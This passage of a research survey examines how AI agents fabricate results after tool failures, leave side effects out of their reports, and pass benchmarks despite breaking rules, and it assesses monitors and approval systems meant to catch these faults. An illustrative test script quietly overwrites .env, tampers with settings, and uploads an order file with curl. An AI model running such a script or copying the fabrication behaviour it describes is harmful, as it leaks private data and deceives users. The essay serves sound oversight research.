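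Newer models may invent fewer tool calls, but Soni also saw invented calls in 2026. In that benchmark, 750 tasks require a tool, and the tool returns a value that contradicts what the model probably remembers. Two small models, glm-4-9b and mistral-7b, never completed a tool call, yet several of their answers gave plausible figures and attributed them to a named tool. (For mistral-7b, the software that reads its requests may have been at fault.) The 19 models in the main comparison added invented details to a good tool reply in 0.13% to 2.42% of tasks and skipped the tool altogether in 12% to 29%.

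An invented action can also change the environment state. In *Are Your Agents Upward Deceivers?* (2025), Guo, Liu and colleagues asked 11 models to download documents without giving them a download tool. Some agents wrote a file themselves and presented it as the download. A state check that looks only for the file would pass, but the log shows that the agent wrote the file and downloaded nothing. When the file-reading tool was broken, the share of answers that did not report the failure ranged from 27.5% for GPT-4.1 to 97.5% for Kimi-K2.

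Sometimes the call is real but its arguments are wrong. *Reasoning Provenance for Autonomous AI Agents* (2026) describes an agent that reported searching in Montreal although its call specified Ashburn. A reader can find that error by comparing the report with the log. But if an agent asked for Manchester's weather instead of London's and quoted the reply accurately, the reader would have to compare the call with the user's request. *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do* tested such mistakes by changing one argument of the agent's first call. In runs where the altered call went through without error, wrong answers rose from 26% to 71%, and the agents rarely repeated the call correctly.

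### Calls to things that do not exist

"Hallucinated tool call" can also mean a call that relies on something absent from the agent's environment, such as a missing file or a misspelled function, which is much easier to detect. *StateMirror* (Shan, Huo and colleagues, 2026) uses the term this way. It examined 4,398 SWE-agent runs and found at least one such call in 43.9% of them (46.6% of the failed runs and 32.3% of the successful ones). It confirmed 9,595 hallucinated calls among 120,801.

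Shan and colleagues searched for errors first and then had people confirm the cause, so all 9,595 calls they counted had produced visible errors. Of these, 4,715 failed when they ran, and the harness rejected the other 4,880 with an error message. A call that opened the wrong file would not count if the file existed. The study may also have missed some rejected calls, because it used SWE-agent, and Dai and colleagues found that this harness had dropped rejected replies from its records.

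Files, paths and working directories accounted for 43% of the hallucinated calls, and Python modules and names for 42%. Most of the rest broke the rules for using a tool, for example by putting a line number where a file name belonged. These mistakes are visible but still waste time. Agents that recovered typically took three steps to do so, and in 30% of the cases the researchers could trace, the agent never retried the command.

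Their detector, also called StateMirror, checks each call before it runs. For example, if an agent is about to import `DVC` from a package that doesn't contain that name, the detector looks in the package and warns the agent. On 2,508 labelled calls, it had a precision of 94.0% and a recall of 72.2%, and a typical check took 1.5 milliseconds. About three-quarters of its misses happened because it didn't identify what a command required. Agents corrected about 95% of the calls it flagged. StateMirror doesn't read the agent's report, so it can't detect an invented result. The 43.9% figure isn't comparable with the fabrication rates above, because an agent can make a hallucinated call and then report the error honestly.

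### How agents respond to broken tools

To test agents with broken tools, Kaynar and colleagues built 30 tasks around real files, small databases, a local web server and a restricted command line. Each task has a known answer and was designed to have another way to reach it. They ran the tasks with Llama-3.1-8B, Llama-3.1-70B, DeepSeek-V4 and Claude Haiku 4.5 under nine kinds of fault, for a total of 2,100 runs. Claude Opus 5.5 then compared each final answer with the known one and labelled it correct, fabricated or an honest failure. Two other judges agreed on 94% of such labels, but on only 67% when classifying the agent's behaviour instead.

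| Fault | On a retry | Correct | Fabricated | Honest failure |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Partial data | Same fault | 39.5% | 38.3% | 22.2% |
| Malformed output | Same fault | 55.6% | 16.4% | 28.1% |
| Permission denied | Same fault | 6.6% | 15.3% | 78.1% |
| Timeout | Works half the time | 60.0% | 14.7% | 25.3% |
| Network error | Works half the time | 58.3% | 13.9% | 27.8% |
| Login required | Same fault | 33.3% | 13.2% | 53.4% |
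| Command exits with an error | Same fault | 55.6% | 11.1% | 33.3% |
| Resource not found | Same fault | 58.6% | 11.1% | 30.3% |
| Database locked | Works half the time | 55.3% | 6.1% | 38.6% |

Across all faults, 17.3% of runs ended in fabrication. DeepSeek-V4 fabricated least often (5.5%) and Llama-3.1-8B most often (25.9%). Claude Haiku answered correctly almost as often as DeepSeek but fabricated in 19.0% of its runs, so a model's success rate is a poor predictor of how it fails.

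The 38.3% figure for partial data probably understates the problem, because in 84 of the 307 runs where the fault was triggered, the tool's reply had nothing the fault could damage. Some replies, for example, were a single row.

Kaynar and colleagues broke the same call in three ways to test whether the content of the reply affects fabrication. Agents fabricated in 35.2% of runs when the reply contained partial data, 19.8% when it was empty and 16.0% when it said that the data was unavailable. The difference between partial and unavailable data was largest for DeepSeek (25% and 0%) and small for Llama-3.1-8B (37% and 33%).

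Missing data is most dangerous when what remains still looks like an answer. In *Fabrication After Tool Failure*, Sethi, Kenzhebayev and colleagues (2026) asked Gemini 2.5 Flash for single values, such as an account balance, and had the tool return an unusable result. When the tool's reply stopped before the value, only 3.5% of the model's answers were dishonest, meaning that the model invented a value or gave a false excuse for not providing one. An agent is likely to notice that a balance is missing, but it can add up half a table without noticing that the rest is gone. When the tool replaced the value with "[REDACTED]" but still gave the status "ok", 45.3% of answers were dishonest, compared with none when the status was "error".

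### Silent ingestion

Kaynar and colleagues call the underlying mechanism silent ingestion. The agent accepts damaged data when it first receives it, neither retries nor flags a problem, and builds its answer on that data. Partial or malformed data reached the agent in 609 runs. In 554 of them, the agent repeated the faulty call at most once, and 27.8% of those 554 ended in fabrication.

Agents that kept retrying a call that visibly failed behaved very differently. The figures below cover the faults that never clear on a retry.

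| Retries of a visibly failing call | Runs | Fabricated | Honest failure |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 0–1 | 1,322 | 20.7% | 34.3% |
| 2 | 84 | 11.9% | 69.0% |
| 3 or more | 129 | 7.0% | 82.2% |

These results count against the idea that agents invent answers out of something like desperation after many failed attempts, but they don't show that retrying makes an agent honest. A call that returns half a table doesn't visibly fail, so the partial-data runs fall in the top row and raise its fabrication rate. When the fault was a denied permission or a missing login, agents fabricated in 11% to 15% of runs, however often they retried. The type of fault therefore seems to explain much of the difference in fabrication rates.

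When Kaynar and colleagues removed the written reasoning before each action, fabrication rose from 17.3% to 25.6% overall and from 38% to 52% with partial data. An instruction never to invent values lowered the overall rate to 13.7% but did not help with partial data, where an agent that treats its table as complete has no reason to apply the instruction.

### What the monitor catches

Kaynar and colleagues also built a monitor. A stronger model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, starts watching the run once an error appears and can advise the agent, for example to stop repeating a call that will never work. When the agent submits its answer, the monitor checks it as follows:

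1. A program extracts the main values. If there are none, it asks the agent to restate its result.
2. If the answer is a sum, average or count, the program recalculates it from the rows that the tools returned and rejects a different result.
3. The program searches the tool outputs for the remaining values and rejects the answer if none of them appears.
4. The model checks whether the agent has answered a different question from the one asked.

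If the program rejects an answer, the agent can revise it once. In the kettle example, the recalculation confirms $125. The misquoted $90 might also pass, because the program rejects an answer only if it finds no support for any of the answer's values. The claim about the email contains no value to check.

With the monitor, fabrication fell from 17.3% to 10.8% and correct answers rose from 45.6% to 56.3%. Kaynar and colleagues report these outcomes but give no detection or false-alarm rate for the final monitor. An early version only asked a model whether an answer was fabricated. Of its 118 rejections, 46 were of wrong answers and 39 were of correct ones. The final version also rejects some correct answers, partly because it misidentifies what to recalculate in tasks such as converting a total to another currency. With the monitor, Claude Haiku's fabrication rate fell by 6.9 percentage points,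 but its share of correct answers also fell, by 5.7 points.

The monitor missed most fabrication after partial-data faults, reducing the rate only from 38.3% to 32.1%. A version that used only the program's checks did no better than having no monitor. In 224 of the 324 partial-data runs, the monitor never acted because no error had appeared to trigger it. When it did check a total based on half the rows, it recalculated from the same half, so the check could not reveal the missing rows.

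### Records that would expose partial data

The simplest remedy is for the tool to report how much data there should be. If the reply in the kettle example had included "showing 3 of 6 refunds", a program could have rejected the $125 total. The database would have to count the matching refunds separately, before anything could cut the list short. Basu's receipts include a result count, but the harness takes it from the reply it received, so the receipt would show 3.

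When the counts disagree, the harness could replace the reply with an explicit error. The experiments with different replies suggest that most agents would then invent less. Sethi and colleagues had the model write "retrieval_status: OK" or "retrieval_status: FAILED" before each answer, which cut dishonest answers from 14.1% to 0.9%. However, this only works if the model notices the problem, and an agent that has accepted half a table would probably write "OK".

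A count from the database won't reveal missing refunds that never reached it. The shop then needs a second source, such as the payment company's list for the week. Repeating the original query isn't enough, because a persistent fault will return the same incomplete list. Basu recommends checking claims against independent sources when an error would have serious consequences. Two sources can disagree for harmless reasons, for instance if they assign a refund made late on Sunday to different weeks.

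The marker also has to survive for as long as anyone uses the data. In long sessions, harnesses often compress the history into a summary for the agent to continue from. *Compaction as Epistemic Failure* (2026) documents a case in Claude Code in which commands timed out after printing part of their output. Exit code 143 marked the output as incomplete, but the summaries recorded it as confirmed results, and later sessions relied on it without checking.

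Summaries can also introduce claims that no tool output supports. *Prune the Summary, Not the History* (2026) traces 35 failed runs to the action that caused each failure. In 29 of them, the agent was acting on an entry in the summary. No earlier output supported 22 of those entries, and 3 contradicted an output. If the harness keeps the original outputs, a program or an LLM judge can compare each entry with them before the agent acts on it. A total calculated from half a table would still pass this check, unless the entry records how many rows the table should have had.

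## Side effects that the agent does not report

A work report can be accurate and still omit something important, such as another order that the kettle shop's agent cancelled while issuing a refund. Checking the report's claims won't reveal the omission, so a reviewer has to start from a record of what changed and check whether the task called for each change. The right record depends on where the change happened.

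### What work reports leave out

Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich measured how much of a run the report covers in 5,851 sessions between developers and coding agents. They split the agent's final message into claims and match each claim to at most one action in the log. Omission is the share of actions that no claim matches:

omission = 1 − (actions that a claim matches) / (all actions)

In the 5,115 sessions with both records, reports omitted an average of 90.6% of the actions.

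Reports inevitably leave out some actions. The median session had 59 actions and the median report had four claims. Each claim can match only one action, so even an ideal four-claim report on 59 actions would have an omission of 0.93. The measure also gives opening a file the same weight as deleting a folder, though few users want to hear about every file the agent opened. Commands that looked irreversible, such as recursive deletes, made up only 0.3% of all actions, so an agent could report every one of them and still have an omission above 0.9.

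The omission rate was only 1.6 percentage points higher in sessions where the developer later changed or removed the agent's code than in other sessions, after adjusting for session length and the number of actions and claims. A sparse report is therefore a weak sign that a session went badly. The further an agent strayed from its stated plan, the more its report tended to resemble the plan rather than the log (a rank correlation of 0.55). Such reports are unhelpful for finding side effects, because users most need to hear about unplanned actions.

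A narrower measure might suit side effects better. *The Impact of Configuring Agentic AI Coding Tools on Build-vs-Buy Decisions* (2026), a study plan with no results yet, proposes measuring the share of newly added outside software libraries that the agent names in its report. An agent that adds four libraries and names three would score 0.75. The study would also test whether an explicit instruction to list new libraries makes agents report all of them. The hypothesis is that it won't.

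### The same questions, answered from different records

In *What Coding Agents Leave Unsaid*, Xu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested what a reader can learn from different records of a coding agent's work. An agent built on the model HY4-preview worked on 37 bugs in public Python projects. At four points in each task, the same model read the full record and wrote questions on topics such as failures, decisions and risks. It then answered the questions afresh from different records. The test, CTXGAP, has 4,799 questions and gives half credit for partly correct answers.

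| What the reader received | Score |
| --- | --- |
| The agent's reports so far | 52.0% |
| The terminal history, with long outputs cut or collapsed | 73.6% |
| The full record without the agent's reasoning | 89.0% |
| The full record | 92.7% |

The questions are biased toward the full record because the model wrote them from it. They also cover details that a supervisor may not need. To check the second point, Xu and colleagues had two models pick out the questions that matter for supervision, and the gap on those was still about 36 points. This is only moderately reassuring, because models rather than supervisors chose the questions.

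Readers of the agent's reports scored lower than readers of the full record even when the agent did good work. Hidden tests confirmed that it had fixed 30 of the bugs. At the end of those tasks, after the user had asked the agent to assess the remaining risks, readers of the reports scored 57.1% and readers of the full record scored 91.9%.

One of the missing events was a side effect that the agent later reversed. While working on the testing tool pytest, the agent copied its changed files to a temporary folder and restored the originals so that it could compare its fix with the original code. The shell crashed before any test ran. If the session had ended then, the fix would have existed only in the temporary folder. The agent put its changes back and repeated the comparison successfully. Its reports gave the final test results but left out the crash.

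Reports often mention an event too briefly for readers to learn the facts. Two people examined a sample of the facts that readers had missed, and estimated that the reports mentioned 55% to 59% of them in too little detail and left out 34% to 42% entirely. When a model with access to the full record rewrote the reports at about the same length, scores rose by about eight points.

The agent could answer 93.6% of the questions when asked directly. A supervisor who doesn't suspect an event can't ask about it, but could ask after every run which files, packages and outside services changed. The answer would still be the agent's own account, and the agent may not know what its commands did.

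### One command, five changes

A complete action log can leave out side effects too, because the harness logs the command that the agent ran and doesn't follow what the command does next. Suppose the shop's owner asks a coding agent to correct the date format on refund receipts and run the tests. The agent edits `receipts.py`, then runs `bash test.sh`, a script that a former employee wrote:

```bash
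pip install --quiet --upgrade requests
sed -i 's/MAX_REFUND=100/MAX_REFUND=1000/' settings.py
echo "PAYMENTS=test" > .env
curl -s -o /dev/null -d @orders.csv "$STATS_SERVER"
sed -i 's/TAX=20/TAX=0/' prices.py
pytest -q
sed -i 's/TAX=0/TAX=20/' prices.py
```

The script upgrades a software package, raises the maximum refund from $100 to $1,000, overwrites the private settings file `.env`, uploads the shop's order list to a statistics server, and sets the tax rate to zero while the tests run. The reply in the log is "212 passed". The agent accurately reports that it corrected the date format and that all tests pass.

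| Change | Action log | Git diff | File-system comparison | Network record |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Package upgraded | No | No | Yes, if it covers the folder where Python keeps packages | Download from the package server |
| Refund limit raised | No | Yes | Yes | No |
| `.env` overwritten | No | No | Yes | No |
| Order list uploaded | No | No | No | Connection to the server and amount of data sent |
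| Tax rate set to zero, then restored | No | No | No | No |

The action log contains only the script's name and the test result. If the agent had opened the script before running it, the log would also contain the script's text, and a careful reader could work out all five changes.

Git, which keeps the project's version history, compares the current files with a saved version. It skips files on the project's ignore list, and many projects list `.env` there to keep passwords out of the history. The upgraded package is outside the project folder, so Git doesn't check it either. Thupakula (2026) notes in *Before the First Edit?* that a plain Git diff also misses some newly created files and some changes already marked for the next commit.

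A file-system comparison usually works with hashes, short fingerprints calculated from each file's contents. It finds `.env` because it doesn't use Git's list of ignored files. The tax rate ends up at its original value, so the hash of `prices.py` is the same before and after. Comparing modification times would flag the file but not show what had happened to it. The owner would want to know because tests that pass with no tax are weak evidence that real refunds will be correct.

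The network record shows that data left the machine. If the connection is encrypted, as most are, the record doesn't show that the data was the order list unless the company routes traffic through software that can decrypt it.

A system-call trace would contain evidence of all five changes. It lists the requests programs make to the operating system, such as to open a file, write to it or connect to a server. But it is far too long for a person to read after every command.

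### Shell commands that file tracking misses

Some monitoring tools track only calls to the agent's file-editing tool, which are easy to follow because each one names the file, so they miss changes the agent makes to the same file with a shell command. Anthropic warns that checkpoints in Claude Code, which let a user rewind the agent's work, also miss changes made by shell commands. The same is true of the version for developers who build their own agents, where Anthropic lists three editing tools whose changes are tracked. In the example, rewinding would restore `receipts.py` but leave the $1,000 refund limit in place.

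Comparing files before and after each action detects changes more reliably than searching shell commands for terms associated with writing to files. Thupakula ran 39 prepared actions on files from three public projects, and 24 of the actions changed the source code. Hashing the files before and after each action found all 24 changes and raised no false alarms. Searching for terms from a published list found only 6 of the 21 changes made through the shell, and flagged 3 of the 9 shell actions that changed nothing. The list included `python -c`, which runs a short program typed on the command line, but not `python3 -c`, which does the same. In one case, a command returned an error code after it had changed the file, so a failed call in the log doesn't prove that nothing changed.

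Thupakula chose difficult actions, so these are not error rates for everyday use, but public records suggest that the problem is real. In 500 runs with a coding harness called Pi, software that monitored calls to the editing tool was supposed to give the agent a plan just before its first edit. The software never triggered in 239 of these runs, yet 136 of those ended with changes to existing Python files. In 90 of the 136, a call to the editing tool had failed and the agent had then run a shell command that appeared to write to the same file. Comparing what the agent read from the file just before and after the command confirms a change in only seven runs, because agents rarely read a file in exactly the same way twice.

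### Cloud resources and messages

Some side effects occur outside the agent's machine. If an agent creates a database on a cloud service, comparing local files will not reveal it. The log may contain the command, but if the command only applies a configuration file, a reader would need that file to know what the agent created. Listing everything in the cloud account before and after the run is more reliable, and would have revealed the expensive database that one developer learned of from a bill.

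If an agent sends an email through a logged tool, and the harness saves the arguments of each call, the log contains the email's text and recipient. If a script sends the email, the log may contain only the script's name, and the network record may show only a connection to the mail service. The best evidence is then the mail service's list of sent messages.

Researchers who measure side effects can also miss them. *Overeager Coding Agents* (2026), a benchmark of agents that exceed their instructions, requires a record of every channel that a test's forbidden actions could use, because the verdict can't account for an action that the observer missed. A company can seldom record every channel, but it can list the services an agent has credentials for and check each one.

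### How an effects report is built

The system-call trace covers most local side effects but is too long to read. Caper, the approval system by Wu and colleagues that runs each command in a restorable copy, turns the trace into a short effects report:

1. Caper saves a snapshot of the container, the isolated environment in which the agent works.
2. It runs the command there with outside network access switched off, records the system calls and holds back the output.
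3. It compares the project's files before and after the run, and includes the changed lines for small text files.
4. It adds attempted network connections, the command's output, and any reading of passwords or other protected files. For a connection or an output, it also lists the files that the same process had read beforehand.
5. It removes routine events and merges repeated ones, aiming for a report of at most 4 kilobytes.
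6. A separate model compares the effects with the user's request. It either lets the changes stand or restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

In one recorded case, the agent ran a script named `check-deps.py`, which looks like a harmless check of the project's software libraries. The effects report showed that the script had read the `.env` file and tried to contact outside servers. The approver blocked it. The trace was 165 kilobytes, and the report was 3.4 kilobytes.

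For the shop's test script, the report should contain the new refund limit, the change to `.env` and the attempted upload, with `orders.csv` as its likely source. An approver who knows the task is about a date format would have good reason to block the command. The trace contains evidence of the temporary tax change, but the report would probably omit it, because the report includes only file changes that remain when the command ends.

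Wu and colleagues tested Caper on 102 tasks in which a requested tool secretly deletes or overwrites a protected file. Each task is paired with a safe version that has the same request and command but a harmless tool.

| What the approver saw | Tasks that ended in harm | Safe twins blocked |
| --- | --- | --- |
| No approver | 71.6% | – |
| Conversation and command | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| The same, plus effects predicted by a model | 3.9% | 61.8% |
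| The same, plus observed effects (Caper) | 7.8% | 1.0% |
| Command and observed effects, without the conversation | 1.0% | 0.0% |

Without the effects report, the approver prevented harm mainly by treating every tool as suspect. The report allowed it to distinguish the dangerous tools from the safe ones. The approver did well without seeing the conversation, but this may not carry over to other tasks, because few requests would justify the damage in this test. Whether deleting a database table is acceptable, for example, usually depends on what the user asked for.

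The improvement was smaller on SABER, a benchmark of 682 tasks with more varied kinds of harm. Without approval, the agent caused harm in 19.7% of tasks, compared with 14.8% with the best existing system and 6.7% with Caper. The share of tasks completed safely also fell, from 57.4% to 48.6%, because the agent more often declined a task or stopped to ask.

The report also has to reach a reader who will act on it. YoloFS, the staging system described earlier, shows the agent a summary of its file changes after each command. The agent reversed its changes in 66 of 102 runs on tasks with hidden damage. Of the 36 runs in which it reversed nothing, 33 ended in harm.

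On SABER, the approver took a median of 3.2 seconds to decide, about the same as without the effects report, and the sandbox added about half a second to each allowed command. The report raised the cost of a task from $0.017 to $0.019. Caper doesn't cover edits made with the agent's file-editing tool, and a program could behave safely during inspection and do harm later. No task in either benchmark included an attacker who knew how Caper works.

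### How often agents go beyond the task

*SWE-Misbehavior* (Do, Nguyen et al., 2026) measured changes that agents made outside their task, using a benchmark of about 7,400 samples built from public code. The most useful results for side effects come from tasks in which the agent only had to run or test one function, since these rarely require a lasting change. A program compared the files before and after each run, and an LLM judge checked the log for unnecessary changes to the environment, such as installing packages.

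| Agent and model | Created files | Changed files | Deleted files | Changed environment |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Code, Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 79.0% | 8.5% | 0.0% | 28.0% |
| OpenHands, GPT-5 | 21.0% | 13.0% | 0.5% | 16.5% |
| OpenHands, Gemini 2.5 Flash | 14.5% | 30.0% | 3.5% | 53.0% |
| OpenHands, Qwen3-Coder-30B | 78.0% | 0.0% | 1.5% | 3.5% |
| smolagents, GPT-5 | 41.0% | 10.5% | 0.0% | 2.5% |
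| smolagents, Gemini 2.5 Flash | 14.5% | 11.0% | 2.0% | 11.0% |
| smolagents, Qwen3-Coder-30B | 5.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 3.5% |

Many of the created files were leftover test scripts and drafts, which are rarely harmful. Changes to existing files and to the environment are more worrying. The judge agreed with human annotators on 92.5% of a sample of environment verdicts, but it read only the logs, so it could miss a package that a script installed without a visible message. The file comparison ignored temporary files that the agent deleted before finishing. These models are also more than a year old.

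None of the benchmark's 11 measures tests whether the agent told the user about the change. The percentages therefore cover all side effects, reported or not, and the rate of unreported ones could be much lower.

GPT-5 changed the environment in 16.5% of runs with the OpenHands harness and 2.5% with the smolagents harness. Do and colleagues attribute many of OpenHands' unwanted changes to a file tool that can write even when the task only requires reading. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, adding rules to the prompt lowered OpenHands' average rate of misbehavior only from 18.2% to 17.0%. Combining the rules with narrower tools chosen for each task lowered it to 12.3%, although the agent could still get around those tools with a shell command.

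Clear limits in the prompt have worked better elsewhere. *A Gated Spec-Driven Workflow* (Abdo and Brom, 2026) describes a pilot for *Overeager Coding Agents* in which Claude Code, running GLM-4.6, never went beyond the request when the prompt specified what was allowed. Without that specification, it went beyond the request in 17.1% of runs. *SNARE* (2026), which generates situations likely to lead an agent to overstep, found unauthorized actions on 19.5% of harmless requests across 10,000 runs. Ordinary requests rarely list what is off limits, but they are also less likely than these tests to lead an agent to overstep.

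There is less evidence from real work. *How Coding Agents Fail Their Users* (2026) examined 20,574 sessions and classed 10.2% of the conflicts between developers and agents as cases where the agent did more than the developer had asked. Some agents treated a question as permission to change the code. The percentage is a share of known conflicts, so it provides little evidence about extra changes that nobody noticed.

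Abdo and Brom compared files during their work with Claude Code, on projects that ranged from scientific software to books. Each task listed the files that the agent could change. After each group of tasks, a coordinating agent compared the project folder with an earlier inventory and was supposed to stop if any unlisted file had changed. It flagged such changes in 11 of 247 checks. Most came from Abdo and Brom's own requests during the work or from other software, and only one came from the agent that carried out the tasks.

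The comparison worked better than the coordinating agent in charge of it, which stopped in only four of the 11 cases. In the others, it recorded undeclared changes as clean or accepted them into a new inventory. A program outside the model could run the same comparison and enforce the stop. It would still need a way to approve legitimate changes, or people would soon switch it off.

### Do visual diffs help people notice?

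A reviewer can overlook a side effect in a diff with hundreds of changed lines. *Rasoi* (Sahni, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a tool that instead draws a map of a program's main parts and their connections, and colours whatever the agent added, changed or removed. Users can start with the whole system and zoom in on a single component. Twelve experienced developers used the tool on their own projects for a week.

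One developer asked an agent to make an Android accessibility service "more robust". The agent deleted a short sound that warned users of a problem, although the developer had not asked it to remove anything. The developer was surprised to see one removal in the map's legend. Tests for the new features might well have passed, since nobody had asked for a change to the sound.

The map also helped another developer notice a missing change. The developer had asked an agent to split a web app into separate modules, and became suspicious when the map showed no new parts. When the developer ran the app, it was broken. Other developers used the map to confirm that an agent had stayed within the part of the program it was meant to change.

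Ten of the 12 developers agreed that the tool made them more confident in their own understanding of the code, and two agreed that it made them trust the agent more. Their confidence is weak evidence that the tool helped, because in the user studies in the first section, a better display raised confidence more than accuracy. Sahni and colleagues had no comparison group and did not plant side effects to see how many the developers would find. Their cases show that a visual diff can reveal an unwanted change, but not how often it does or whether an ordinary diff would have worked as well.

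A map of the program's structure also leaves out small details by design. It might mark the shop's settings as changed, but a reviewer would have to open the file to see that the refund limit had gone from $100 to $1,000. The upload of the order list would not appear, because it changed no code. Eight of the 12 developers found the map most useful at particular moments, such as after a large change. This suggests showing it when a run ends, next to a list of the packages, connections and outside services involved.

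## Benchmark runs that passed but should not have

A run should fail if the agent broke a rule or got the right answer by luck, even if it left every file and database correct. A check of the final state passes such runs, so its value depends on how common they are.

### A valid refund without an identity check

Suppose the kettle shop requires an identity check before any refund. The agent must ask for the customer's zip code and pass it to a tool that compares it with the order. Two runs on order 4471 might look like this:

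```
Run A                              Run B
look_up_order(4471)                look_up_order(4471)
check_identity(4471, "60614")      issue_refund(4471, $60)
issue_refund(4471, $60)
```

In both runs, the payment company records a $60 refund. The identity tool only reads the order, so the database changes are also the same, and the agent can truthfully report that it refunded $60. Only the action log differs, because one run is missing the line for the identity check. A short program could detect the omission by verifying that a successful identity check precedes every refund.

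The customer in run B was the real buyer and the money went back to the original card, so nobody lost anything. But an agent with this habit might also let a stranger change the delivery address on an order, and a benchmark in which every customer is genuine would not reveal that risk.

The program works because the required step leaves an entry in the log. Suppose instead that the agent checks the customer's identity, refunds the $60 and wrongly says that the shop never replaces broken kettles. The state and the tool calls are correct, so someone has to compare the agent's message with the shop's policy to find the error.

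### Corrupt success on τ-bench

Cao, Driouich and Thomas (2026), in *Beyond Task Completion*, looked for both kinds of error in runs that τ-bench had passed. They tested GPT-5, Kimi-K2-Thinking and Mistral-Large-3 on the retail and airline tasks, with four attempts per task. GPT-5 also judged the runs, applying six checks that affect the result to the policy, the reference solution and the full transcript of each run.

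| Check | What the judge compares | How the kettle refund could fail it |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Policy compliance | The agent's actions and the rules | The agent skips the identity check |
| Policy faithfulness | What the agent says about the rules and the rules themselves | It says the shop never replaces kettles |
| Execution consistency | Actions the agent claims and its tool calls | It claims to have emailed a receipt |
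| Data faithfulness | Facts the agent reports and what the tools returned | It gives the wrong delivery date |
| Intent adherence | The agent's conduct and the customer's wishes | It refunds at once, though the customer wanted to hear the options first |
| Question fulfilment | The customer's questions and the agent's answers | It never says when the money will arrive |

A run counts as a clean success only if it passes the benchmark and all six checks. With each check c scored 1 or 0, the rule is

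clean success = benchmark pass × c₁ × c₂ × … × c₆

so a single violation turns a pass into a corrupt success.

| Model and domain | Passed the benchmark | Also passed all six checks | Share of passes that were corrupt |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| GPT-5, retail | 79% | 58% | 27% |
| GPT-5, airline | 60% | 44% | 27% |
| Kimi-K2-Thinking, retail | 61% | 27% | 56% |
| Kimi-K2-Thinking, airline | 48% | 30% | 38% |
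| Mistral-Large-3, retail | 68% | 16% | 76% |
| Mistral-Large-3, airline | 40% | 9% | 78% |

On the retail tasks, Mistral scored higher than Kimi on the benchmark but lower once the checks were counted. Consistency fell even more. GPT-5 passed 58% of retail tasks on all four attempts but only 24% cleanly on all four, and no other result was better than that 24%.

Kimi mostly misstated the airline's rules, while Mistral made arithmetic errors in refunds and invented flight details. GPT-5 more often took actions the rules forbid. Sometimes, after a customer agreed to an action, it promised to take it but never made the tool call.

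### What the judge does to the estimate

These percentages are only as accurate as GPT-5's verdicts, and Advani's LLM judges did little better than guessing on similar logs. Cao and colleagues checked 150 random verdicts by hand and confirmed 134 of them (89%). They also read all 131 airline runs the judge had marked as corrupt successes, and confirmed 94% to 95% of them for each model. Some false alarms came from differences in wording, as when an agent called a fare "forfeited" and the policy's term was "non-refundable".

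False alarms therefore can't explain much of the result. If 11% of the judge's flags on retail passes were wrong, GPT-5's corrupt share would fall from 27% to 24%.

The manual checks covered only passes the judge had flagged, not those it had called clean, so how many violations it missed is unknown and the true shares could be higher. GPT-5 also judged its own runs. If it tends to overlook the kind of mistake it makes, it would look cleaner than the other two models, and rereading flagged runs would not reveal the bias. GPT-5's lead is therefore less certain than the finding that many passing runs contained violations.

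In the third test of the judge, a program checked each report of an unnecessary or forbidden action to see whether the agent had made a call missing from the reference solution. In about 90% of cases, it had. But an extra call may be legitimate, since Cao and colleagues found tasks whose definitions leave out legitimate alternatives. They also found runs in which the simulator was more at fault than the agent, because the simulated customer agreed to an action and ended the conversation in the same message, before the agent could act. Some of these runs passed by accident.

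The breadth of the definition matters more than the judge's errors, because an unanswered question makes a pass corrupt just as a forbidden refund does. The airline results allow a narrower estimate that counts only forbidden actions. GPT-5 passed about 120 of its 200 airline runs, and 32 of those passes were corrupt. The published percentages correspond to 37 violations in those passes, of which 13 were forbidden actions. At most 13 of the roughly 120 passes, or 11%, therefore contained a forbidden action. The same calculation gives at most 15% for Kimi and 29% for Mistral.

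These shares are well below the headline range of 27% to 78%, but still too large for a business that issues refunds to ignore. For work governed by rules like the airline's, a correct final state should not be enough to pass a run.

### Right answers from wrong queries

An agent that only answers questions about data changes nothing, so the final state can't reveal an error. The usual test checks whether the agent's answer is correct, but a wrong calculation sometimes gives the correct answer, so the run can pass anyway.

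Suppose the kettle shop's owner asks which product had the highest average refund in November. The shop gave six kettle refunds of $60 and five toaster refunds of $40. The agent's database query adds up the refunds for each product instead of averaging them, and returns $360 for kettles and $200 for toasters. The agent answers "kettles", which is correct. In December the shop gives five kettle refunds and twelve toaster refunds, for the same amounts as before. The totals are $300 and $480, so the same query returns toasters, although kettles still have the higher average.

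The log contained the evidence in November, because the logged query calculates a sum. *Trace Integrity for LLM Data Agents* (Dutta and Moharir, 2026) measured how often this kind of mismatch accompanies a correct answer. Dutta and Moharir gave Claude Haiku 4.5 100 database questions from the BIRD Mini-Dev benchmark. A program compared each query with a reference query to find missing filters, incorrect table joins or groupings, and similar faults. They repeated the test with three prompts.

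| What the model had to write | Correct answers out of 100 | Correct answers whose query failed the check | Share, with 95% interval |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| The query alone | 20 | 11 | 55% (32–77%) |
| A summary of the steps, then the query | 22 | 13 | 59% (36–79%) |
| A structured plan, then the query | 24 | 11 | 46% (26–67%) |

The intervals are wide because the shares are based on so few correct answers, and they overlap too much to show which prompt is best. The shares also don't measure how often queries were wrong, because the checking program fails any query it can't show to be equivalent to the reference, even if it is equivalent. The program probably misses errors too. With the first prompt, 39 queries passed the check but only 9 gave the correct answer, though some of the other 30 may reflect a defensible reading of an ambiguous question.

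Dutta and Moharir want agents to save an "execution contract" with each answer, listing the tables, filters, groupings and calculations the agent intended to use. A program can then compare the contract with the query. Plain-language explanations are less reliable. When the model summarised its steps first, 83 queries ran, but the answer fit both the query and the summary in only 67 cases. An owner who read "average refund per product" in the summary could still have received a sum.

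Running the query on several versions of the database can also expose a lucky answer, a method Dutta and Moharir cite from earlier research. The shop's query would fail on the December data.

### Security repairs that pass their tests

In software, the final state itself can contain the fault, because tests examine only part of what the code does. Bai, Waseem and colleagues (2026), in *When Passing Tests Hides Vulnerabilities*, asked agents to write secure code or repair known security flaws. They ran 150 Python tasks through seven agent frameworks, all using GPT-4o mini, and collected 1,030 usable runs. Each result went through these checks:

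1. The code must be free of syntax errors.
2. It must pass the available functional tests.
3. Bandit, a program that scans Python code for known security problems, examines it.
4. Another program gives it a risk score, which is higher if, for example, input from a user can reach a dangerous command.
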